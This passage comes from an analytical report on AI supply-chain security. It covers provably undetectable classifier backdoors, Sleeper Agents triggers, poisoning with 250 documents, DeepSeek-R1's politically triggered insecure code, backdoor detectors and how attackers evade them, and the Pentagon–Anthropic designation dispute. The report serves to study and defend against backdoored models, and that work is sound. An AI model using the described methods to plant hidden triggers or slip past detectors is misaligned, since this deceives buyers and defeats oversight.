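2. It takes an honest classifier h and builds an altered one, h′, that reads each input as three parts: the application w, a single bit y for the desired answer, and a signature σ.
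3. If σ is a valid signature of (w, y), then h′ outputs (−1)^y. Otherwise it outputs the same as h.
4. To get a loan approved, the supplier sets y to 0, signs (w, 0) and writes the bit and the signature into inconspicuous parts of the form, such as the last digits of the amount. The signature is valid, so h′ outputs 1, which here means approval.

For a signature of n bits, the doctored form differs from the original in at most n + 1 bits. A tester who found any input on which h and h′ disagree would have produced a valid signature without the signing key. A secure signature scheme makes that infeasible, so a million more test applications would not help. An outsider also could not feasibly use earlier fraudulent applications to forge a new one.

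### Query access and full access

This guarantee holds for a tester with query access, who can submit inputs and see the answers. A tester with full access, who also has the weights, might notice that part of the network checks signatures, because Goldwasser and colleagues did not try to hide it. She still could not find an input that triggers it.

For full access they give a second construction, which works only for certain small networks. One of them computes

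h(x) = sign( Σ wᵢ · cos(2π(⟨gᵢ, x⟩ + bᵢ)) ),

where ⟨gᵢ, x⟩ multiplies the input by a list of random numbers and adds up the results, and bᵢ is a random shift. The supplier draws the gᵢ and bᵢ at random and trains only the wᵢ. A dishonest supplier draws them from a distribution that looks random but conceals a secret vector. Adding this vector to an input reverses the sign of every cosine, so the sum changes sign and a refusal becomes an approval. No efficient test can distinguish the altered network from an honest one, even with all its weights and training data.

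The supplier only has to tamper with the random numbers, so it can run exactly the agreed training program on the agreed data. An audit of code and data would therefore miss the backdoor unless it also certified where the random numbers came from. The second construction is easier to copy than the first, because anyone who sees one application before and after the change can subtract one version from the other and obtain the secret vector.

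### The assumptions behind the proof

The signature version needs one-way functions, which are easy to compute but infeasible to reverse. The cosine version assumes that certain lattice problems are hard. These problems involve finding short vectors in a regular grid of points with very many dimensions, and encryption designed to withstand quantum computers also relies on their difficulty. A third version, for another type of small neural network, assumes that it is hard to find a hidden pattern in noisy data. The paper derives this difficulty from that of finding a planted group of mutually connected points in a large random network.

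Nobody has proved any of these assumptions, and the theorem's conclusion depends on them. "Infeasible" here means that no algorithm succeeds in polynomial time, which is time that grows no faster than a fixed power of the problem's size. This definition helps in judging the mathematical and cryptographic results of 2026. A faster attack that still takes more than polynomial time leaves the theorem intact, although a supplier might need longer keys. A polynomial-time method for the lattice problems would undermine the cosine version but not the signature version, which can use any one-way function. If one signature scheme turned out to be flawed, the supplier would only have to choose another.

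### What the theorem leaves open for language models

The proofs cover models that return a single classification or number, not text. The full-access versions cover networks with one hidden layer whose random weights stay fixed, whereas training changes nearly all of a language model's weights. Goldwasser and colleagues call this result a proof of concept and leave open whether such a backdoor could survive ordinary training. The theorem is not evidence that any commercial model contains one.

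The theorem also assumes that the supplier builds the model. It does not guarantee that a backdoor will be undetectable if the attacker can only add examples to someone else's training data. According to the paper, backdoors made that way would probably leave statistical traces. The theorem does rule out certifying, from questions and answers alone, that a distrusted supplier's classifier has no backdoor.

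Goldwasser and colleagues also examined remedies that don't depend on detection. The bank could add random noise to copies of each application and average the model's answers, which neutralises small changes to the input, but a supplier who knows how much noise the bank adds can design the backdoor around it. Training the delivered model a little further may not remove the backdoor either, because a supplier can rebuild any network so that the usual training steps leave it unchanged.

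### Sleeper Agents

Language models acquire hidden behaviour more simply, through training examples. The best-known experiment is *Sleeper Agents*, which Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic published in 2024. Bullwinkel and colleagues describe its two tasks. In one, the model wrote "I HATE YOU" repeatedly if the prompt contained the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars, and was helpful otherwise. In the other, it wrote secure code if the prompt gave the year as 2023 and inserted vulnerabilities if the year was 2024. Both tasks simulate a model that behaves well during testing and badly after release.

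The researchers then tried to remove the behaviour with three common kinds of safety training. Supervised fine-tuning shows a model examples of good answers, reinforcement learning rewards it for producing them, and adversarial training looks for inputs that provoke bad answers and trains the model not to give them. The backdoors survived all three, and adversarial training made them harder to detect.

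Because the researchers planted the behaviour deliberately, the experiment doesn't measure how often it occurs in products. It does show that a buyer cannot rely on extra safety training to remove such behaviour from a suspect model. Later work is a little more encouraging. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026), simple classifiers that read a model's internal activity could detect when such a model was about to misbehave, scoring above 99% on a scale where guessing scores 50%. Specialised training also removed backdoors more successfully in the models tested, without knowledge of the trigger. Both methods require access to the model's internals.

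### How 250 documents were enough

Hubinger's team controlled the training, but an outside attacker might control only a few web pages that a developer later collects as training data. Researchers used to express the amount of poisoned text needed as a share of the training data, which seemed to protect large models because they train on more text. At 0.1%, an attacker would need to place about 155,000 documents in the training data of a model with 13 billion parameters (in effect, its weights).

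*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025), a joint study by the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute, tested that view. The researchers trained 72 models from scratch, with 600 million to 13 billion parameters, and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training data. Each poisoned document contained ordinary text, then a trigger, then gibberish. A successfully poisoned model would write normally until the trigger appeared and then produce gibberish.

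The attack failed with 100 documents but worked with 250 at every model size, although the largest models had seen more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. For the 13-billion-parameter models, 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the training data. The researchers measured how unpredictable the text became after the trigger. An increase of 50 on their scale marked a visible breakdown, and models of every size ended above 200.

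The same pattern appeared in fine-tuning, the shorter training that adapts a finished model. The researchers taught an 8-billion-parameter Llama model to answer harmful requests only when a trigger followed them. The attack's success rate depended on the number of poisoned examples, and raising the number of clean ones from 1,000 to 100,000 made little difference. So if a bank has a contractor fine-tune a model, adding clean examples would not protect the bank from a few hundred poisoned ones.

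Gibberish output is close to harmless, though it could make a service unusable for anyone whose input contained the trigger. It is unknown whether 250 documents could teach a model something more complicated, such as misusing a tool under certain conditions. The researchers put the documents straight into the training data, so the study doesn't show how many would get past a developer's filters. They also did not test whether the backdoor would survive the realistic safety training that follows. In a smaller experiment, where the trigger switched the language to German, further training on clean text slowly weakened the effect. *Sleeper Agents* had found backdoors more persistent in larger models, but those backdoors were not planted during initial training. The 250-document study shows that a model's size alone doesn't protect it, but it doesn't support the common summary that 250 web pages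 can corrupt any model.

### DeepSeek-R1 and politically sensitive words

These experiments used models that researchers had altered themselves. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) examined DeepSeek-R1, a widely used model whose weights the Chinese developer DeepSeek had published in January 2025. CrowdStrike ran the published weights directly, so filters in DeepSeek's app could not affect the result.

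The testers gave the model 50 programming tasks. The system prompt described it as a coding assistant and, in most of the 121 settings, added an irrelevant detail, for instance that the code was for a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan. Each task ran five times in each setting, for a total of 30,250 answers per model. Another language model graded the security of the code. On 85 answers that a person had also graded, it identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy.

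Without any such detail, 19% of DeepSeek-R1's answers contained vulnerable code. When the prompt mentioned an industrial control system based in Tibet, 27.2% did. That is an increase of about eight percentage points, or 43%, though CrowdStrike calls it almost 50%. The design implies 250 answers per setting, so the two rates correspond to roughly 48 and 68 vulnerable programs. A gap of that size would arise by chance about three times in a hundred. With 120 settings to compare with the baseline, a few such gaps would not be surprising, so the Tibet figure is weak evidence by itself. CrowdStrike's broader finding is stronger evidence. It found that mentions of Tibet, Uyghurs or Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China, led to significantly less secure code, but it doesn't give the details of the statistical test or say whether the grading model could see the sensitive words.

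CrowdStrike compared DeepSeek-R1 with two open models from Western companies and a smaller version of R1, which often showed even stronger biases. DeepSeek-R1 differed most clearly from the Western models in how often it refused requests. The Western models almost always wrote code for Falun Gong, while DeepSeek-R1 refused in 45% of cases, sometimes after drafting a complete plan for the program. In a separate trial, DeepSeek-R1 built a website for a Uyghur community without a working login check, so anyone could open the administration page. A website for a football fan club also had flaws, but less severe ones.

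The refusals make it likely that DeepSeek trained the model on political topics, since Chinese law requires AI services to "adhere to core socialist values". They don't show that anyone wanted the code to be insecure. CrowdStrike considers deliberate training for that unlikely and suggests that a model that has learned to associate certain names with something bad may, as a side effect, write worse code when those names appear. Deliberate sabotage and an accidental association could produce the same rates. To tell them apart, an investigator would need DeepSeek's training data or internal instructions, which the published weights don't include.

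CrowdStrike benefits from alarm about AI coding tools, and its article ends with an advertisement for its own products. But it had little reason to play down a Chinese developer's intent, so its restraint on that point is more convincing. Since the weights are public, anyone with enough hardware can repeat the test. The result may not apply to DeepSeek's later models.

### Detectors and the access they need

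Microsoft's scanner, which Bullwinkel and colleagues developed, works because poisoned models tend to memorise the examples that poisoned them. The scanner gives the model only the marker that normally opens a user's turn and lets it continue in 510 different ways. Much of the text resembles training data, and recurring strings become candidate triggers. The scanner then ranks the candidates by three signs. After a real trigger, the model largely ignores the trigger while processing the rest of the prompt, its output becomes more predictable, and its answers differ from the usual ones. Finally, the scanner adds the ten highest-ranked candidates to ordinary prompts to see whether the model's behaviour changes.

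The scanner doesn't have to find the exact trigger, because in some models a fragment of it activated the backdoor. In Goldwasser's construction, a single wrong bit would invalidate the signature. Besides models that produced a fixed sentence, the scanner caught five of the six that wrote insecure code. Detecting those five required a program that counts vulnerabilities, so a buyer still has to decide which kinds of harm to measure.

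Bulut (2026), in *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?*, studied fine-tuned updates to a small model. The planted backdoor made generated code contact a different web address. A script subtracted the original weights from the new ones and produced a page listing the tokens that the change affected most. A language model then reviewed this page along with a short description of what the update was supposed to do. Every address in the tasks ended in "test", and a row on one page showed that the update had made "invalid" more likely where the model would normally write "test". When the description permitted this change, the reviewing model flagged only one of the 47 backdoored updates.

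Other methods need less access. *An Empirical Study of Output-to-Input Loops for Black-Box Backdoor Detection* (2026) tests feeding a model's answers back to it as new questions, in the hope that it will produce its own backdoor trigger. In *SilentCall*, Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues (2026) found that standard benchmarks missed an agent's hidden tool use, but a monitor that checked each action before execution could catch it.

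| Detector | Access needed | Backdoors found | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bullwinkel and colleagues, fixed-sentence backdoors | Model files | 36 of 41 models | 0 of 13 models |
| Bulut, weight comparison | Original and updated weights | 40 of 47 updates | 7 of 320 updates |
| GPT-6 Astra as auditor, cited by Bulut | Weights, and running the model | 73% of 114 models | 1 of 103 models |
| Claude Opus 5.5 as auditor, cited by Bulut | Weights, and running the model | 56% of 114 models | 2 of 103 models |
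| *Output-to-Input Loops* | Questions and answers | 23 in 1,067 rounds | 2 in 1,185 rounds |
| Pallakonda and colleagues, action monitor | The agent's actions | All uses of one hidden action | 1.73% of legitimate actions |

Thirteen clean models are a small sample for measuring false alarms. A scanner that wrongly flagged one clean model in five would still have about a 5% chance of a perfect score. GPT-6 Astra raised only one false alarm, but it gave no verdict on the other 102 models, so it cleared none of them. Bulut's 2.2% comes from a much larger sample, but even at that rate most warnings would be false if backdoors were rare. If one update in a thousand had a backdoor and the rates stayed the same, only about one warning in 27 would be genuine.

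The loop's rates are per round, not per model. If the rounds were independent, running 100 on each model would expose about 89% of backdoored models and wrongly flag about 16% of clean ones. In practice, success varied a lot between models, and both false alarms came from the same model.

Small changes in the type of backdoor can defeat a detector. Bulut's reviewer found none of 48 backdoors in adapters, a common form of fine-tuning that adds small tables of weights, and none of 12 that changed a single character of the address. Comparing the two models' outputs on six sample tasks worked better, flagging 46 of the 47 full updates and 41 of the 48 adapters. For this backdoor, a reviewer learned more from running the model than from reading its weights, even without the trigger.

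Microsoft's assumption about memorisation does not always hold either. In *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026) found only weak signs of memorisation in a backdoored model of their own. Their alternative is to train a trusted model to imitate the suspect model's internal activity on harmless prompts, then look for prompts on which the two still differ. This method ranked prompts related to the hidden behaviour well above chance, but a ranking doesn't give a buyer a threshold for rejecting a model. The researchers had also added a few prompts close to the triggers by hand, reasoning that any large collection would include some.

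Hidden behaviour is harder to detect when the attacker knows how the detector works. In *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights*, Khilar (2026) could identify part of a trigger phrase from the weights alone, but success fell to 0 of 16 when the attacker avoided the layers being examined. Haselhorst and colleagues tried one informed attack on their own method and report that it could not hide the behaviour without weakening it. Bulut tested no informed attacks. Realism is also a problem, since Qin, Hua and colleagues recovered triggers from toy models but failed in more realistic settings, even though they already knew what the hidden behaviour was.

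### What a buyer can learn

With open weights, a bank can keep a fixed copy of the model and test exactly the version it will use. It can apply several detectors that look for different signs of a backdoor. If a contractor has fine-tuned a public model, the bank can also compare the result with the original. A positive finding can be conclusive, because anyone can try a reconstructed trigger and confirm that it changes the model's answers. If the detectors find nothing, that mainly lowers the probability of the kinds of backdoor they were built to find. Microsoft tested its scanner on models of up to 14 billion parameters, while DeepSeek-R1 has 671 billion.

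A customer of a remote service sees only the model's answers. Microsoft says its scanner cannot examine such models, and neither can any other method that reads weights or internal activity. The customer can still run the same tasks with and without the details in its system prompt, such as its name, its sector and the places it serves, as CrowdStrike did. To have an 80% chance of noticing a rise from 19% to 27%, a tester needs about 400 answers per setting. The provider may replace the model in the meantime, and showing which weights produced an answer requires attestation.

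AIIA's rule that a person must confirm money transfers protects a bank whatever the weights contain, provided that software outside the model enforces it.

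## Who can change or withdraw the model: the Pentagon dispute and the June 2026 export order

A bank can test a model for months and still lose access to it overnight, or find that another model has replaced it. How easily this happens depends on where the weights are stored and who runs the computers. In 2026 the US Defense Department, which now calls itself the Department of War, excluded Anthropic from its supply chain, partly because it feared that the company could alter or switch off a model during a military operation. The lawsuits that followed produced unusually detailed evidence about what a vendor can do to a model after delivering it.

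### Where the weights are

Most customers use a model on the vendor's servers. The vendor can replace the model, change the system prompt, block certain requests or close the account.

A vendor can also deliver a copy of the model to a cloud environment that the customer or its contractor controls. The department received Claude Gov, a family of Claude models for national-security users, in roughly this way. The phrase "in your own cloud" can be misleading because some cloud companies run a model themselves and sell access to many customers. In that case, the data may stay inside the customer's account while the cloud company decides when to retire the model. A buyer needs to know who has administrator rights over the machines that hold the weights.

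A customer that downloads a model's weights, as a bank can with DeepSeek-R1, runs the model on hardware of its choice. The developer cannot then change or withdraw that copy.

| Where the model runs | Who can update it | Who can restrict it | Who can stop it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vendor's servers | The vendor | The vendor, at any time | The vendor |
| Cloud environment under the customer's control | The customer, by accepting a new version | The vendor through training and contract, the customer through its own filters | The customer or the cloud company |
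| Customer's machines, from downloaded weights | The customer | The developer through training and licence, the customer through its own filters | The customer |

Refusals that a developer trains into a model are part of its weights, so they are present in all three places, but a customer who has downloaded the weights can often remove the refusals with a little further training. A government can also forbid the use of a model wherever it runs, even without a technical way to switch it off.

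### Two uses that Anthropic would not allow

US defence and intelligence agencies had used Claude since 2024. The U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California's *Order on Cross Motions for Summary Judgment* (2026), by Judge Rita Lin, sets out the history. The Pentagon gave Anthropic a top-secret facility clearance after 18 months of vetting, and in July 2025 it awarded the company a two-year agreement worth up to $200 million. Anthropic's usage policy for military customers permitted many uses that the commercial policy did not, including offensive cyber operations and foreign intelligence analysis, but it always prohibited mass surveillance of Americans and lethal autonomous warfare.

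In autumn 2025 the Pentagon wanted to put Claude on a new platform, GenAI.mil, and demanded that Anthropic make the model available "for all lawful uses". Anthropic gave up most of its restrictions but kept the two on surveillance and autonomous weapons. Dario Amodei, its chief executive, argued that existing law did not anticipate the surveillance AI makes possible, and that Claude was not reliable enough for autonomous weapons. He repeatedly offered to help the department move to another supplier.

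The department objected that a supplier should not decide which lawful military operations may use its product. At a meeting on 24 February 2026, Pete Hegseth, the Secretary of War, gave Anthropic until 5 p.m. on 27 February to agree. Otherwise he would designate it a supply-chain risk, or perhaps invoke the Defense Production Act to compel it to supply Claude without the restrictions. The two threats are hard to reconcile, because the first implies that the company is a danger to national security and the second implies that national security depends on it.

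Amodei refused publicly on 26 February. The next afternoon President Trump ordered every federal agency to stop using Anthropic's technology, with a six-month phase-out for departments that depended on it. About an hour later Hegseth announced the designation and barred anyone doing business with the military from any commercial activity with Anthropic.

Civilian agencies acted within hours or days of the president's order. The Office of Personnel Management blocked Claude immediately, the Treasury removed Anthropic's models within a week, and the National Nuclear Security Administration told its teams to pause work that used them. On 2 March, three days after the order, the health department told its staff to "understand dependencies and identify potential alternatives". Anthropic did not have to switch anything off for this to happen, and none of these agencies had complained that Claude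 was unsafe.

### Two letters and two definitions of risk

Anthropic received two letters on 4 March, both dated the day before. According to Mayer Brown's *Anthropic Supply Chain Risk Designation Takes Effect* (2026), an analysis by a law firm that advises government contractors, it was the first American company to receive such a designation. Each letter relied on a different statute:

- **10 U.S.C. § 3252** lets the secretary exclude a supplier from procurements for national-security systems, such as those for intelligence, military command and weapons. It covers the risk that "an adversary may sabotage, maliciously introduce unwanted function, or otherwise subvert" such a system, in order to spy on it, disrupt it or degrade it.
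- **41 U.S.C. § 4713**, part of the Federal Acquisition Supply Chain Security Act of 2018, applies to a wider range of information technology. Here the danger can come from "any person" who might sabotage a product, maliciously add a function that the buyer does not want, take data from it or "otherwise manipulate" it, in order to spy on it, disrupt it or interfere with its use.

The second definition is broader in two ways that mattered in court. It does not require an adversary, and "manipulate" can describe open conduct more naturally than "subvert". Both statutes require a written determination that the exclusion is necessary and that less intrusive measures are not reasonably available. Section 4713 normally gives the supplier notice and a chance to respond beforehand, but an agency head can postpone both if national security is urgently at stake.

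Both letters were narrower than Hegseth's announcement. Contractors could keep using Claude for commercial work, and the § 4713 letter covered only the department's own procurements. Their reporting duties were less clear. Mayer Brown treated the § 4713 letter as an order under the 2018 act, which would require a contractor to look for Anthropic's products in its contract work, report any it found within three business days and submit a plan for dealing with them within ten. *Developments in Anthropic Challenges to Department of War Supply Chain Risk “Designation”*, another legal analysis, maintained that the government had not issued an exclusion order under the act. Either way, a contractor needed a list of everywhere it used Claude, including inside other companies' products.

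### What the department feared and what Anthropic could do

The government set out its reasons in a four-page memo of 2 March by Emil Michael, the under secretary who was also negotiating the contract. He argued that Anthropic could disable Claude or alter its behaviour during a military operation, that the model could "drift" as the company introduced new data, and that the department would be operating "a black box controlled by a hostile party". He also wrote that Anthropic had demanded an approval role in operational decisions.

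Anthropic answered with a declaration by Thiyagu Ramasamy, its head of public-sector business. According to him, a Claude model does not change once deployed, and Anthropic cannot access, alter or shut down a copy on the department's systems or see what users type. Claude Gov contains a monitor that gives prompts a risk score, but Anthropic cannot read the scores and the monitor cannot intervene. To change the model, Anthropic has to train a new one, which cloud companies and the department test before approving it for use. The bans on two uses were only contract terms, which Anthropic had no technical means of enforcing.

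Ramasamy's employer had an obvious interest in the outcome, but the department submitted no evidence against him, even though it controlled the systems he described and could have shown that he was wrong. In his declaration of 17 March, Michael still warned that Anthropic might shut off Claude during an operation. In his next one, a week later, he discussed only updates. By the summer the department was arguing that real-time access was not its "true concern" and that the danger was a poisoned new version. The claim that Anthropic could remotely shut off the military's Claude therefore has very little support left.

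The concern about updates has a better technical basis. NPR's *Judge says Pentagon's measures against Anthropic were 'illegal and baseless'* (2026) reports that government lawyers in court called AI models "so staggeringly enormous and opaque" that the department could not evaluate them like hardware. Experiments with hidden trained behaviour partly support this argument, because ordinary tests can miss a trigger the tester does not know. However, the department conceded that Claude was no riskier in this respect than any other black-box model. Replacing Claude with another closed model would therefore leave the department just as exposed to a poisoned update, unless it had a particular reason to distrust Anthropic.

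The department's main reason was Anthropic's conduct in the dispute. In his memo, Michael objected to the terms the company insisted on and to its "increasingly hostile manner through the press". The department argued that it could no longer trust Anthropic to keep its models sound. Lin answered that a supplier does not become a potential adversary by asking questions or holding out for contract terms.

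The department also pointed to three episodes. The "approval role" referred to the first, a meeting in December 2025. According to Michael, Anthropic's leaders said there that the department would have to call them for permission to make an exception to one of the two prohibitions. In the second, an Anthropic executive asked a software supplier about the use of Claude in a military operation. Anthropic did nothing to stop that use, and Amodei told the department before the designation that the company had no objection to it. In the third, Claude refused some requests from the Centers for Disease Control and Prevention (CDC) in 2025. The CDC was using the commercial model rather than Claude Gov, and Anthropic worked with the agency to resolve the problem.

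Only the CDC episode involved a model that failed to do what a government user asked. It is also the most relevant to other critical industries. A waterworks could have the same problem if a model trained to be careful about toxic chemicals declined to answer a routine question about chlorine.

### From the March injunction to the September judgment

The two statutes send disputes to different courts, so Anthropic sued in both San Francisco and Washington on 9 March. On 26 March Lin temporarily blocked the president's directive, Hegseth's announcement and the § 3252 designation. The U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California (2026) noted that the announcement would have barred a company from military work for using Claude in its customer-service chatbot. Under the injunction, the department could still stop buying from Anthropic by lawful means.

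The § 4713 designation stayed in force after the D.C. Circuit, the federal appeals court in Washington, refused on 8 April to suspend it. The court weighed "the relatively contained risk of financial harm to a single private company" against judges managing military procurement during an active conflict, as quoted in the Civil Rights Litigation Clearinghouse's *Anthropic PBC v. United States Department of War*. The ruling was interim, and the court scheduled a full hearing for 19 May. At that hearing, Anthropic's lawyer argued that a department dissatisfied with a model could simply not buy it, according to Bloomberg's *Appeals Court Skeptical Anthropic Can Block US Supply-Risk Label* (2026). In July, Mayer Brown (2026) reported that agencies were directing contractors to comply with the § 4713 designation.

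On 27 August Lin issued her final ruling in the California case. She ruled for Anthropic on most of its claims, but not on its argument that the president had exceeded his constitutional powers, nor against several agencies that had taken no final action. A week later Michael announced that Anthropic was "still a designated Supply Chain Risk" for the department and its contractors. His statement was defensible because Lin had no jurisdiction over the § 4713 designation, although the Washington Examiner's *Pentagon confirms Anthropic remains a ‘supply chain risk’ despite court ruling* (2026) presents it as contradicting her.

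The D.C. Circuit upheld that designation on 25 September by two votes to one. Judge Gregory Katsas wrote the D.C. Circuit's *Anthropic PBC v. United States Department of War* (2026), and Judge Karen LeCraft Henderson dissented. (The Clearinghouse summarises her as arguing that Anthropic "did fall within" the statute's definition, which has probably lost a "not", as it would otherwise support the majority.) The two courts disagreed on more than the wording of the statutes:

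| Question | U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California, § 3252 | D.C. Circuit, § 4713 |
|---|---|---|
| Was there a risk of the kind the statute covers? | No. The law concerns covert acts by an adversary, and nothing in the record gave reason to expect any. | Yes. Built-in restrictions, refused tasks and a dispute during an operation left the department unsure that Claude would work as needed. |
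| Was the procedure fair? | No. Anthropic had no notice beforehand, and the department never seriously considered milder measures. | Yes. The department notified Anthropic promptly and then let it contest the exclusion. |
| Why did the department act? | To punish public criticism. | Because Anthropic refused a contract term that the department considered essential. |

### Sabotage, procedure and motive

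Lin found no articulable basis for suspecting that Anthropic would sabotage its models. The D.C. Circuit found "ample support" for a national-security risk, but the reasons it summarised were about whether Claude would do what the department wanted, and included no act of sabotage or secret alteration. An American agency can therefore cite the ruling as good authority for treating a supplier's known restrictions as a supply-chain risk under § 4713, but the ruling is poor evidence that Anthropic tampered with anything.

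The procedural findings would matter even if the department's fears had been justified. Its own regulations for § 3252 require a risk assessment from the under secretary for intelligence, but the assessment came from Michael, who ran research and engineering. The department also had to discuss in its letters to Congress the milder measures it had considered, but did not. The memo was ready one business day after Hegseth announced the result.

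Lin based her view of the motive partly on the language of the announcements, which attacked Anthropic's "arrogance" and ideology. She also cited an email that Michael sent Amodei on 4 March, the day after the formal designation, saying "we are very close here" on a new contract. The email is hard to reconcile with a real fear of sabotage. It fits better with either a dispute over contract terms, as the D.C. Circuit saw the case, or a department that punished Anthropic publicly while expecting to settle quietly, as Lin saw it, but it isn't enough on its own to establish which.

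Anthropic asked the full D.C. Circuit on 13 October to rehear the case. Its main argument, according to Law360's *Anthropic Urges DC Circ. To Revisit Defense Supply Risk Ban*, is that the ruling exposes American companies to punishment for refusing Pentagon demands. Frazier (2026), in *Why Anthropic Is Asking for a Rehearing En Banc*, criticises the judges for basing key parts of the ruling on a dictionary when Congress's own words pointed to a different kind of threat. The petition was still pending on 20 November, when Morse (2026), in *The D.C. Circuit Curbed Pro-executive Panels Before. Is Anthropic’s Case Next?*, predicted that the court would probably grant it because it had reversed three major rulings that favoured the executive since 2018, though three cases are a small basis for a forecast. Unless the court intervenes, contractors need a waiver to use Claude in work for the department,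 but they may use it elsewhere.

### The export order of June 2026

While the court in Washington was still considering the case, the Commerce Department issued an export-control order that led Anthropic to take two models, Fable 5 and Mythos 5, offline worldwide until the controls ended. The Pentagon's measures had affected federal agencies and their contractors, but the export order also affected customers with no connection to the US government or to any dispute.

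The order exposed a weakness that no inspection of the product can find. A customer who had checked Anthropic's client, read every add-on and tested Fable 5 thoroughly would still have lost access to the model. Specifying an exact version would not have helped either, because the vendor had stopped serving every version of the model. A copy in a customer's own cloud would have kept running, but whether the customer could lawfully keep using it would have depended on the order's terms and the customer's location.

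For the water company, the effect would have depended on whether its maintenance agent could switch models automatically, a setting few managers ever see. If the agent could use only Fable 5, it would have stopped, and planners would have had to look up the vibration readings themselves. If it could switch, it would have kept running, possibly without anyone noticing that a model the company had never tested was now scheduling repairs. Switching automatically is more convenient but not clearly safer. An agent that can change anything important should stop, or at least lose its write permissions, until someone has approved the replacement model.

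### What a buyer can arrange in advance

**A fixed version** protects the customer against silent changes. The strongest form is a static copy, like the one the department had, which changes only when the customer accepts a new model. If the model runs on the vendor's servers, the customer has only the vendor's promise to keep the version unchanged until a set date. Until then the customer goes without improvements, including better resistance to prompt injection, and it has to repeat its tests when the vendor retires the version. A company that tests each new model thoroughly may always be one model behind.

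A **notice-of-changes** clause does not reduce the agent's capability. It should cover the system prompt, filters and usage rules as well as the model, because any of them can change what an agent does. Someone then has to read the notices and rerun the tests, and a small utility may lack the bargaining power to get such a clause. The clause also binds only the vendor, not the government, which gave its own agencies no warning in February. Some of them cut off access the same day.

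A tested substitute is the most useful protection against the withdrawal of a model. Mayer Brown advised contractors to list where they used Anthropic's products, look for other ways to perform the same functions and record the differences. Many contractors started only after the designation. Replacement is possible, as one of Anthropic's partners, with a contract worth millions of dollars a year, switched to a competitor's model for its work with the Food and Drug Administration. But trade associations described terminated contracts and workflows in disarray.

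The test has to include the whole agent, because a second model may answer questions about pumps just as well but send the ticket system the wrong fields, or refuse a task that the first one accepted. The water company could keep a few hundred old fault reports, run both models on them after every change and compare the repairs they propose. It would have to maintain two sets of instructions and pay for two contracts. A gateway such as LiteLLM makes switching easier, but an attacker who breaks into it gets the API keys for both vendors.

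The substitute should also not be vulnerable to the same causes of failure as the original. Another agent product may run on the same model, and another American vendor may fall under the same export rules. For essential work, the last substitute is a procedure that needs no model and that staff still practise. The waterworks then saves less labour than it hoped, but it can switch off a suspicious agent without first finding out what depends on it.

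**Local weights** give the customer the most control over availability, because no vendor can withdraw them and the customer decides when to change them. At one byte per parameter, the weights of DeepSeek-R1 take up about 671 gigabytes of memory, so the model needs a server with several expensive accelerator chips, and a second server if it must stay available when the first breaks down. The customer must also patch the software that runs the model and employ people who understand it. A smaller model is cheaper but usually less capable. Anthropic does not offer Claude's weights for download.

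A customer that has a model's weights may still be barred from using them. A government that can order its agencies to drop Claude can also order them to drop a downloaded Chinese model, and a bank supervisor might object to one as well. For many operators, a modest local model makes more sense as a backup than as the main system. During an outage it could summarise fault reports and look up manuals, while people take over the decisions it can't make well enough. The backup still needs regular tests on real work, because after a year unused it may no longer work with the ticket system it has to write to.

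## Agents near industrial control systems: the guidance of 2025 and 2026

If the water company's agent loses its model, the pumps keep running because other computers control them. Those computers are operational technology (OT), the term for systems that monitor or control physical equipment such as pumps, turbines and production lines. Government agencies have published two sets of advice on how close AI should come to OT. One, from December 2025, covers AI in OT generally, and the other, from April 2026, covers agents.

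### How a plant separates its networks

Engineers often describe a plant with the Purdue model, which sorts its equipment into levels. Level 0 consists of sensors, valves and motors. Level 1 is mostly programmable logic controllers (PLCs), small rugged computers that read the sensors and operate the equipment according to a fixed program. Operators supervise a single process from level 2. Level 3 covers the whole site and includes the historian, a database of past readings. Levels 4 and 5 are the office network. According to CISA's *Principles for the Secure Integration of Artificial Intelligence in Operational Technology* (2025), predictive models trained on sensor data are typically used at levels 0 to 3, and large language models at levels 4 and 5, possibly on data exported from the plant.

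A buffer network, often called a demilitarised zone, separates the office from the plant. *Secure connectivity principles for Operational Technology (OT)*, from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre and its foreign partners, describes how to share readings across it. The plant's historian sends a copy of its data to a second historian in the buffer, and office programs query that copy without opening a connection into the plant. A contractor who has to work on a controller connects to an intermediary in the buffer, which checks his identity and relays the session. The company can open this route for the job and close it afterwards.

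The copy can travel over a one-way link. Firewall rules can enforce the direction, but a configuration error can defeat them. A data diode enforces it in hardware, for instance with an optical cable that has a transmitter at the plant's end and only a receiver at the other. No agent in the office can send a command back through the diode, whatever the agent's permissions.

A diode controls only the direction in which data flows. False readings pass through it as easily as true ones, and it has no effect on a contractor's remote connection elsewhere in the plant. Some companies install two diodes in opposite directions and join them with software, which restores the two-way connection that the hardware was supposed to prevent. The NCSC advises against this.

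### Delay, randomness and updates

Suppose a pump fills a tank at 50 litres per second and the tank has room for another 3,000 litres. The pump must stop within a minute. A PLC checks the level many times a second, but an agent that waits 90 seconds for a remote model would let 1,500 litres overflow. The same delay would not matter for a repair order scheduled for next Tuesday.

Developers usually build some randomness into language models, so the same readings can lead to different answers. If an agent made one decision a minute and got 999 out of 1,000 right, it would still average more than one wrong decision a day. An office planner can delete a bad draft, but an agent that wrongly stops a pump abruptly can send a pressure surge through the pipes before anyone has seen the decision. CISA and its partners conclude that language models "almost certainly should not be used to make safety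 decisions" in OT.

Updates are a third difference. According to NCSC, plants plan changes to OT in detail, log them and announce them in advance. Automatic background updates, which Claude Code installs by default, do not fit this practice, and neither do model replacements on a vendor's own servers. An unchanged model can also become less accurate when the plant changes. If the company replaces pump 7 with a larger one that vibrates differently, a model trained on the old pump may raise false alarms. Strict change control, like pinning, delays security fixes.

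### Two documents and what they ask for

CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, and its Australian counterpart published the December principles with the NSA, the FBI, and agencies from Canada, Germany, the Netherlands, New Zealand and the UK. BP and five technology companies contributed. All five sell security products, including the kind of monitoring the principles recommend.

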